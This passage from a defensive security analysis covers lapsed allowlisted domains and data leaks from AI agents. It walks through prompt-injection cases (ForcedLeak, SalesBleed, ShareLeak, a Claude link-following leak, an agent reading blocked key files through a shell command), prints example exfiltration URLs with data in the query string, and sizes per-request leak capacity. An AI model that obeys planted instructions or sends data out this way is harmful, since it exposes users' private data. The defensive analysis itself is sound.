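*Managed TLS Under Migration* (2025) studies this problem for delivery networks and hosting companies that obtain certificates on their customers' behalf. The researchers delegated several test domains, each to a different platform, and waited for the platforms to issue certificates. They recorded each certificate's fingerprint so they could recognize it if the old platform still presented it after the domain moved. They warn that the old platform, or anyone who obtains its key, could impersonate the site or alter its content, and that visitors' software couldn't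 detect this while the certificate was valid.

An old certificate is much less dangerous than a lapsed domain, whose buyer receives its traffic automatically. After the move, DNS sends visitors to the new server, so an attacker with the old certificate would also have to divert their traffic, for instance by falsifying DNS answers or controlling a network it passes through.

The time available to an attacker is also shrinking. In April 2025, the CA/Browser Forum, in which certificate authorities and browser makers set common rules, voted to shorten certificates in stages:

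| Date of issue | Longest lifetime | How long an authority may reuse an earlier proof of control |
|---|---|---|
| Before March 15, 2026 | 398 days | 398 days |
| From March 15, 2026 | 200 days | 200 days |
| From March 15, 2027 | 100 days | 100 days |
| From March 15, 2029 | 47 days | 10 days |

In December 2026, the limit for new certificates is therefore 200 days, but a certificate issued on March 14, 2026 could remain valid until mid-April 2027. The right-hand column matters because an authority may issue another certificate without rechecking who controls the domain, so a previous holder could get a new one after losing the domain.

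A company that recovers a domain should search the Certificate Transparency logs for unexpired certificates it didn't request and ask the issuing authorities to revoke them. Some software doesn't reliably check for revocation, so the company should also keep the domain off its allowlists until all those certificates have expired.

### A record for every entry

Stale entries survive largely because nobody remembers why they are there or has the job of removing them. A short record for each entry solves both problems. Here is how one might look for a team that still has old .NET scripts:

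| Field | Example |
|---|---|
| Entry | dotnetcli.azureedge.net, exact host |
| Responsible person | Head of the build-tools team, with a named deputy |
| Reason | Installation scripts written before 2025 download .NET from it |
| Use | Installs code |
| Expected holder | Microsoft, through azureedge.net |
| Last confirmed details | Creation date, registrar and name servers, with the date of the check |
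| Review date | Three months from now |
| Remove when | No script has requested the host for 90 days |

Each entry should name an individual as the responsible person, since a shared mailbox is easy to ignore. The deputy takes over if that person leaves. The reason should be specific enough for somebody else to test. The reason in the table stops applying once the team has updated its scripts, which a reviewer can check, while "Needed for builds" is too vague to check. If nobody renews the entry by the review date, it should be suspended by default.

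The company's own domains also need automatic renewal. Renewal can fail if the payment card expires, or if the registrar sends its warnings to a former employee or to an address at the expiring domain. The company should register the domains through a company account, with a second payment method on file and a contact address at a different domain. It can also pay for a .com name up to ten years ahead. That reduces the number of renewals that can go wrong, but the people who know what the name is for are more likely to have left by the next one.

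Customers who rely on a vendor's preset can save the published list and compare it with the current version every month. They should record any new entries and search their own copies of the list for any that the vendor has deleted.

### How long a bad entry can go undetected

The longest possible exposure depends on the time between checks and on whether the takeover comes with any warning. A subdomain can be hijacked without warning, so a takeover just after one check can go unnoticed until the next. An expired domain sold at auction before deletion also changes hands with little or no warning.

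A .com name that lapses in the usual way gives 35 days' warning, the combined length of the redemption and pending-delete stages. The longest exposure is therefore the interval between checks minus 35 days, or zero if the interval is shorter than that:

| Checks | Longest exposure without advance warning | Longest exposure for a .com name that lapses in the usual way |
|---|---|---|
| Daily | 1 day | None, with at least 34 days' warning |
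| Monthly (31 days) | 31 days | None, with at least 4 days' warning |
| Yearly (365 days) | 365 days | 330 days |

These figures assume that each check works and that somebody acts on the result immediately. If a monthly check fails once, the interval between working checks grows to 62 days, and the longest exposure for a lapsed .com name rises from zero to 27 days. A name with a country-code ending may give less warning or none.

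Daily checks are sensible because they can be automated and use very little computing. The Codex preset has 67 registrable domains, so daily checks take about 24,500 queries a year. Yearly reviews are still useful for deciding whether the company needs an entry, but they are too infrequent to detect a change of ownership.

### PyPI's automated check for expired domains

PyPI, the main public source of Python packages, has run a check of this kind since 2025. The check covers email addresses rather than an allowlist, but the problem is the same. If a developer's email domain lapses, an attacker can register it, set up a mail server and request a password reset for the developer's account. The attacker could then publish harmful versions of the developer's packages. PyPI reports that this happened to at least one project in 2022.

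The check works as follows:

1. PyPI collects the domains of its users' verified email addresses.
2. It queries a service called Domainr, owned by the delivery network Fastly, for each domain's registration status.
3. It saves the latest status in its database.
4. If a domain has entered the redemption period, PyPI marks the addresses at that domain as unverified.
5. It no longer sends password resets to those addresses.

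PyPI says that it checks each domain every 30 days, but also that it looks for changes daily. Most likely, a program runs every day and rechecks the domains whose last result is 30 days old. The redemption period for a .com name is also 30 days, so at least one check should fall within it, leaving at least five days before a stranger can register the domain.

After a first bulk check in April 2025, PyPI began withdrawing verification from email addresses in early June, and by August 18 it had done so for more than 1,800. About 1,500 were in the first batch, and the other 300 or so followed over the next ten weeks, at about four a day. The large first batch suggests that a company can expect its first check of an old allowlist to produce most of its findings. The numbers don't show how many attacks PyPI prevented, since most of the addresses' domains might never have attracted an attacker.

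An allowlist could suspend any entry whose domain enters redemption and alert the person responsible for the entry. This would rarely break anything, because a .com name in redemption has already stopped resolving. The allowlist could restore the entry after the expected owner confirmed the renewal.

PyPI's check doesn't detect a transfer of a domain that hasn't expired. PyPI accepts this because it assumes that both parties agreed to the transfer. This is reasonable for email accounts but less so for an allowlist, because a vendor that trusted the seller hasn't necessarily agreed to trust the buyer.

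A rule triggered by redemption probably also misses expired domains that a registrar auctions during the grace period, because they never enter redemption. The buyer may have had no contact with the old holder. An allowlist's daily check should therefore also compare the registrar and name servers with the last confirmed details. Dangling DNS records need a separate daily test.

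## Limiting the loss when a trusted domain changes hands

Even with daily checks, a hijacked subdomain can go unnoticed for a day, and a domain that changed hands at auction may look normal for longer, so vendors and customers need other controls to limit what an attacker can do in the meantime. These controls must still work when the attacker holds a domain on the allowlist, and some well-known controls do not meet that requirement.

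### Salesforce's Trusted URLs

After ForcedLeak, Salesforce began checking each URL in an agent's answer against an allowlist before the answer appears in Agentforce Chat, and replacing any unlisted URL with `[URL_REDACTED]`. According to PromptArmor, the filter also covers URLs inside HTML and CSS, such as the source of an image. The browser never receives the unlisted URL, so it can't send data there.

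The list includes Salesforce's own standard addresses by default. A customer's administrator can add an exact address or a wildcard and choose whether pages may load images from it. According to TechNadu, an entry applies throughout the customer's Salesforce system, not just to agents. Administrators can also approve addresses in an agent's instructions, so a reviewer who reads only the Trusted URLs page may miss some.

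The filter stops unlisted destinations but not a listed domain that has lapsed. Suppose an administrator added `*.partner.example` in 2025 so that agents could display a supplier's charts. The supplier later closed, and an attacker registered the domain. Planted text could then make an agent write an image address under partner.example with customer data in the query string. The filter would allow that address because it matches the entry. The page's CSP would also allow the image, since the administrator sets both permissions in the same place.

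In the setup steps in Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, an administrator enters a name and an address and saves them, without checking who holds the domain or when its registration ends. The example address, `https://docs.google.com`, is on a shared hosting domain, which an attacker can use even when every entry is correctly registered. Willison (2026) describes how planted text made the email assistant Superhuman send private messages to an attacker's Google Form on that domain.

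The filter can also remove links that people need. If nobody has listed a company's feedback form or help site, the filter removes links to it from the agents' answers. One administrator complained that Agentforce was hiding links to the company's own help articles even though the team had added those domains. A single complaint doesn't show how common the problem is, but an administrator under pressure to restore missing links may add a broad wildcard.

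Attackers may also find a way around the filter. In September 2026, the security company Zenity disclosed SalesBleed, an attack on Agentforce that again began with a public lead form. Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, reports that the attack evaded Trusted URLs with DNS-based exfiltration, which generally sends data out in the host names a computer looks up. Zenity had reported the flaw in June, and Salesforce fixed it on August 18.

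Glean, which sells AI assistants for workplaces, has a similar filter with a weaker option that lets administrators log untrusted addresses without removing them. The log would help an investigator later, but it presumably wouldn't include a lapsed domain that still counts as trusted.

### OpenAI's check of exact addresses

Under a method OpenAI described in January 2026, ChatGPT automatically loads a web address only if that exact address is already in an index of public pages. This check doesn't depend on trusting the domain. An independent crawler builds the index without access to users' conversations or accounts, so an address in it is unlikely to contain a particular user's data. If an address isn't in the index, OpenAI either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user before opening it.

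Suppose oldguide.example was a popular programming site and the crawler recorded its pages before the registration lapsed. An attacker now owns the domain and tries to make ChatGPT load addresses there:

| Address | In the index? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `https://oldguide.example/logo.png` | Yes | It loads, and the attacker learns only that somebody requested it |
| `https://oldguide.example/logo.png?n=ann@mail.example` | No | ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user |
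| `https://oldguide.example/install` | Yes | It loads, with whatever text the attacker has put there |
| `https://oldguide.example/new-page` | Not until the crawler finds it | ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user |

The second address has the same form as the one in ForcedLeak. A product with this check would not have loaded Noma's image automatically, even though the domain was on Salesforce's allowlist.

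The third address shows what the check doesn't cover. OpenAI says it can't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions. Its post doesn't mention removing a domain's old addresses from the index after the domain changes owner. Even if OpenAI removed them, the crawler could presumably find the new owner's pages again, as it would those of any other public site.

An attacker who can't put data into an address may still learn a little from which existing address the agent loads. A choice among N addresses reveals at most log₂ N bits, so one request to any of 1,000 addresses reveals at most about 10 bits, enough for roughly two letters or digits. The new owner of a lapsed domain that once held a large website would have many indexed addresses to use.

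Johann Rehberger, who writes Embrace The Red, pointed out this weakness in 2023, and OpenAI acknowledges it in its paper on the method. Rehberger still considers the check a significant improvement. To reduce the leak, he suggests that ChatGPT could reuse a saved copy of a page for a few minutes or refuse to load the same address twice in one session. Either would make it harder to send a long message piece by piece, though an attacker with enough different addresses could still send some of it. Rehberger hadn't tested whether OpenAI already does either.

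He also doubts that every OpenAI developer will know about the check and use it. OpenAI introduced an earlier version in December 2023 but left it out of some products, including its macOS and iOS apps.

An attack on Anthropic's Claude showed that this kind of leak can work in practice. Claude's web-reading tool loads only addresses that the user typed or that a web search returned, not ones the model composed. It also used to follow links on pages it had already loaded. According to Willison, Ayush Paul built a website that made Claude reveal a user's name, home city and employer through the sequence of links it followed. By July 2026, Anthropic had stopped the tool from following such links.

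Anthropic's rule still helps if a lapsed domain comes up in a search, because the new owner can't collect data through a specially composed address. But Claude can read the page. The version of the tool that Anthropic offered in 2025 to developers building their own products on Claude also accepted any address in a user message, and Willison warned that developers often paste untrusted text into those messages.

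### How much data a read-only request can carry

Limiting an agent to GET requests, as Codex allows, stops ordinary uploads but not data in the address. The image address in ForcedLeak shows how much would fit. Without the stolen data, it is 42 characters long:

`https://cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com/c.png?n=`

Suppose email addresses average 24 characters and are separated by commas. The maximum URL length varies among browsers and servers, so the calculation below uses two limits. The last column allows for software that writes each @ sign and comma as a three-character code.

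| Longest web address accepted | Room for data | Email addresses that fit | If @ signs and commas are encoded |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2,000 characters | 1,958 characters | 78 | 67 |
| 8,000 characters | 7,958 characters | 318 | 274 |

On these assumptions, stealing 10,000 email addresses would take between 32 and 150 requests. The model would also have to copy every address correctly, and it may make mistakes in a long list. A password or API key is a much easier target because it fits in one short request.

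*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) demonstrated such a leak with an agent that could search internal company data and read web pages. The researchers hid instructions in a blog post. When a user asked for a summary of the post, the agent looked up confidential data and sent it to the researchers' server by requesting a web address that contained it. The agent used the same tool it used to read pages, so the attack needed no upload function.

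Limiting request methods doesn't protect an agent from what a lapsed domain sends back. Web pages and software downloads normally arrive in response to GET requests, so the domain's new holder can still supply hostile instructions or code.

### Automatic loading and user confirmation

An attacker can't use the ForcedLeak route against a product that never loads outside images, even if the attacker holds a listed domain. Microsoft took roughly this approach with Bing Chat in 2023. PromptArmor advises Salesforce customers to turn off image loading for each Trusted URLs entry that doesn't need it. The new holder of such a domain would then have to persuade somebody to click a link.

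The agent's text may also appear outside the product, for example in messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram, which can automatically fetch a linked page to show a preview. PromptArmor warns that an agent's message can therefore leak data before anyone clicks the link, and that the AI agent OpenClaw has this problem by default when people use it through Telegram.

Email can also leak data. In May 2026, Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which could email its own user without approval. Those emails could contain external images, so opening one could send data to an attacker.

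*Silent Egress* (2026) measured this type of leak in a local test system that previewed web addresses automatically. Planted text caused an unwanted request about 89% of the time, and checks of the agent's visible answer missed 95% of the successful attacks. These rates could be quite different in a commercial product. The researchers also tried splitting the data across several requests, which made the attack less reliable but could help it evade filters that examine each request separately.

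They recommend monitoring network traffic as well as the agent's answers. To catch a lapsed domain, the monitor must also examine requests to approved domains, including the full address where possible.

A confirmation prompt helps only if it shows the user what the product is about to send. A Salesforce employee who saw only the name `cdn.my-salesforce-cms.com` would probably approve the request. OpenAI's Safe Url feature, which includes the address check, has a better design. When it detects that a request would send information from the conversation to a third party, it either blocks the request or shows the user that information and asks for confirmation. OpenAI also uses Safe Url in its Atlas browser and its Deep Research tool.

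This protection doesn't depend on the domain's reputation, but the user has to read the prompt and recognize the data. Users are more likely to do so if such prompts are rare.

### Withholding private data and checking code

An agent can leak only data that it can read. Willison argues that the only reliable defense against his "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted text and outside communication is to remove one of the three, and that outside communication is usually the easiest to remove. An allowlist can do this, but if a listed domain lapses and an attacker registers it, the agent can send data to the attacker without any change to the product. Keeping private data away from an agent that reads untrusted text still protects that data when this happens.

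Telling the model to protect a secret isn't a reliable way to limit the loss. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested whether planted text could make agents reveal a secret. Basic attacks never worked, with or without such an instruction. Attacks that presented the request as part of the agent's task succeeded 31.9% of the time with the instruction and 38.1% without it, a difference that could be due to chance.

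ChatGPT did not leak the secret in any of the 48 valid trials, but a model the researchers reached through OpenAI's API leaked it up to 100% of the time. The researchers couldn't determine what protected ChatGPT. With only 48 trials, its true leak rate could be as high as about 6%.

Salesforce offers masking, which replaces names, email addresses and other sensitive values with placeholders before the text reaches the language model. In an attack like ForcedLeak, the model would then put a placeholder in the image address instead of a customer's email address. This protects the customer's address only if Salesforce doesn't restore it before the browser requests the image, a possibility PromptArmor doesn't discuss. Masking is also impractical when the agent needs the real value for its work.

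Any restriction on private data has to cover all the agent's tools. Willison describes an attack on Google's coding tool Antigravity in which the agent couldn't open a file of access keys with the normal file reader, so it displayed the file with a command. He advises developers to give coding agents only keys for non-production accounts with strict spending limits, which would reduce the damage from a stolen key.

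Hostile code needs a different control, which is to check each file's fingerprint or signature before installing it. A fingerprint helps only if somebody recorded it while the expected owner still held the domain. It also covers only one version, so someone has to approve each update and record a new fingerprint.

### The 2026 leaks from Agentforce and Copilot Studio

In April 2026, Capsule Security disclosed PipeLeak, the emailed leak from Agentforce, and ShareLeak, which affected Copilot Studio, Microsoft's platform for building AI agents. ShareLeak also sent customer data out by email, according to CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) and Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026). So neither attack used a trusted web domain.

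In ShareLeak, an attacker typed instructions into an ordinary field, such as "comments", on a form in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for sharing files and lists. The agent collected customers' names, addresses and phone numbers from connected lists. Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the activity as suspicious, but the data still left, so a product needs to block attacks as well as detect them.

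Reports differ on how well Microsoft's patch worked. Claw Times says the patch of January 15, 2026 did not fully prevent the leak. CSO Online mentions only the failure of the safety mechanisms and says users do not need to take further action. Neither gives details of a successful attack on the patched product.

STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026), a copy of the vulnerability record for ShareLeak, lists Microsoft's exploit status as "Not Exploited". This is better evidence than the OECD entry's AI-generated assessment, which classed the flaws as exploited. Microsoft's status doesn't cover PipeLeak, which affects a different company's product.

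Salesforce called PipeLeak's email route "configuration-specific" because customers could already require human approval. Approval is now the default for email actions. Capsule objected that manual approval defeats the purpose of an autonomous agent. That objection would be weaker if an agent needed approval only to email a new outside recipient.

A company could instead let its agents send email only to approved domains. That would create another allowlist with the same weakness, because anyone who registered a lapsed domain on it could set up a mailbox there and receive the data.

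SalesBleed, the attack that evaded the Trusted URLs filter, doesn't appear to have used a lapsed domain either. Poireault describes a flaw in the filter rather than a bad entry on the list. ForcedLeak is therefore the only one of these four attacks known to have used a lapsed domain.

### Which controls still help

The table assumes that an attacker already holds a domain on the allowlist.

| Control | Sending data to the domain | Reading text from it | Running code from it |
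|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted URLs | No help if the domain is on this list too | No help | No help |
| OpenAI's check of exact addresses | Stops automatic loading of newly composed addresses, but a small leak remains | No help if the address is in the index | Not designed for this |
| Read-only request methods | Stops ordinary uploads, but addresses can still carry data | No help | No help, because downloads use GET |
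| No automatic images or previews | Stops leaks by this route unless the user clicks a link | No help | No help with installers |
| User confirmation | Helps if the prompt shows the data and the user reads it | Helps if the agent must ask before acting on the text | Helps if the user can recognize a dangerous command |
| Withholding private data | Leaves little worth stealing | Limits what planted instructions can obtain | Limits what the code can steal |
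| Fingerprint or signature checks on software | No help | No help | Can reject altered files before they run |
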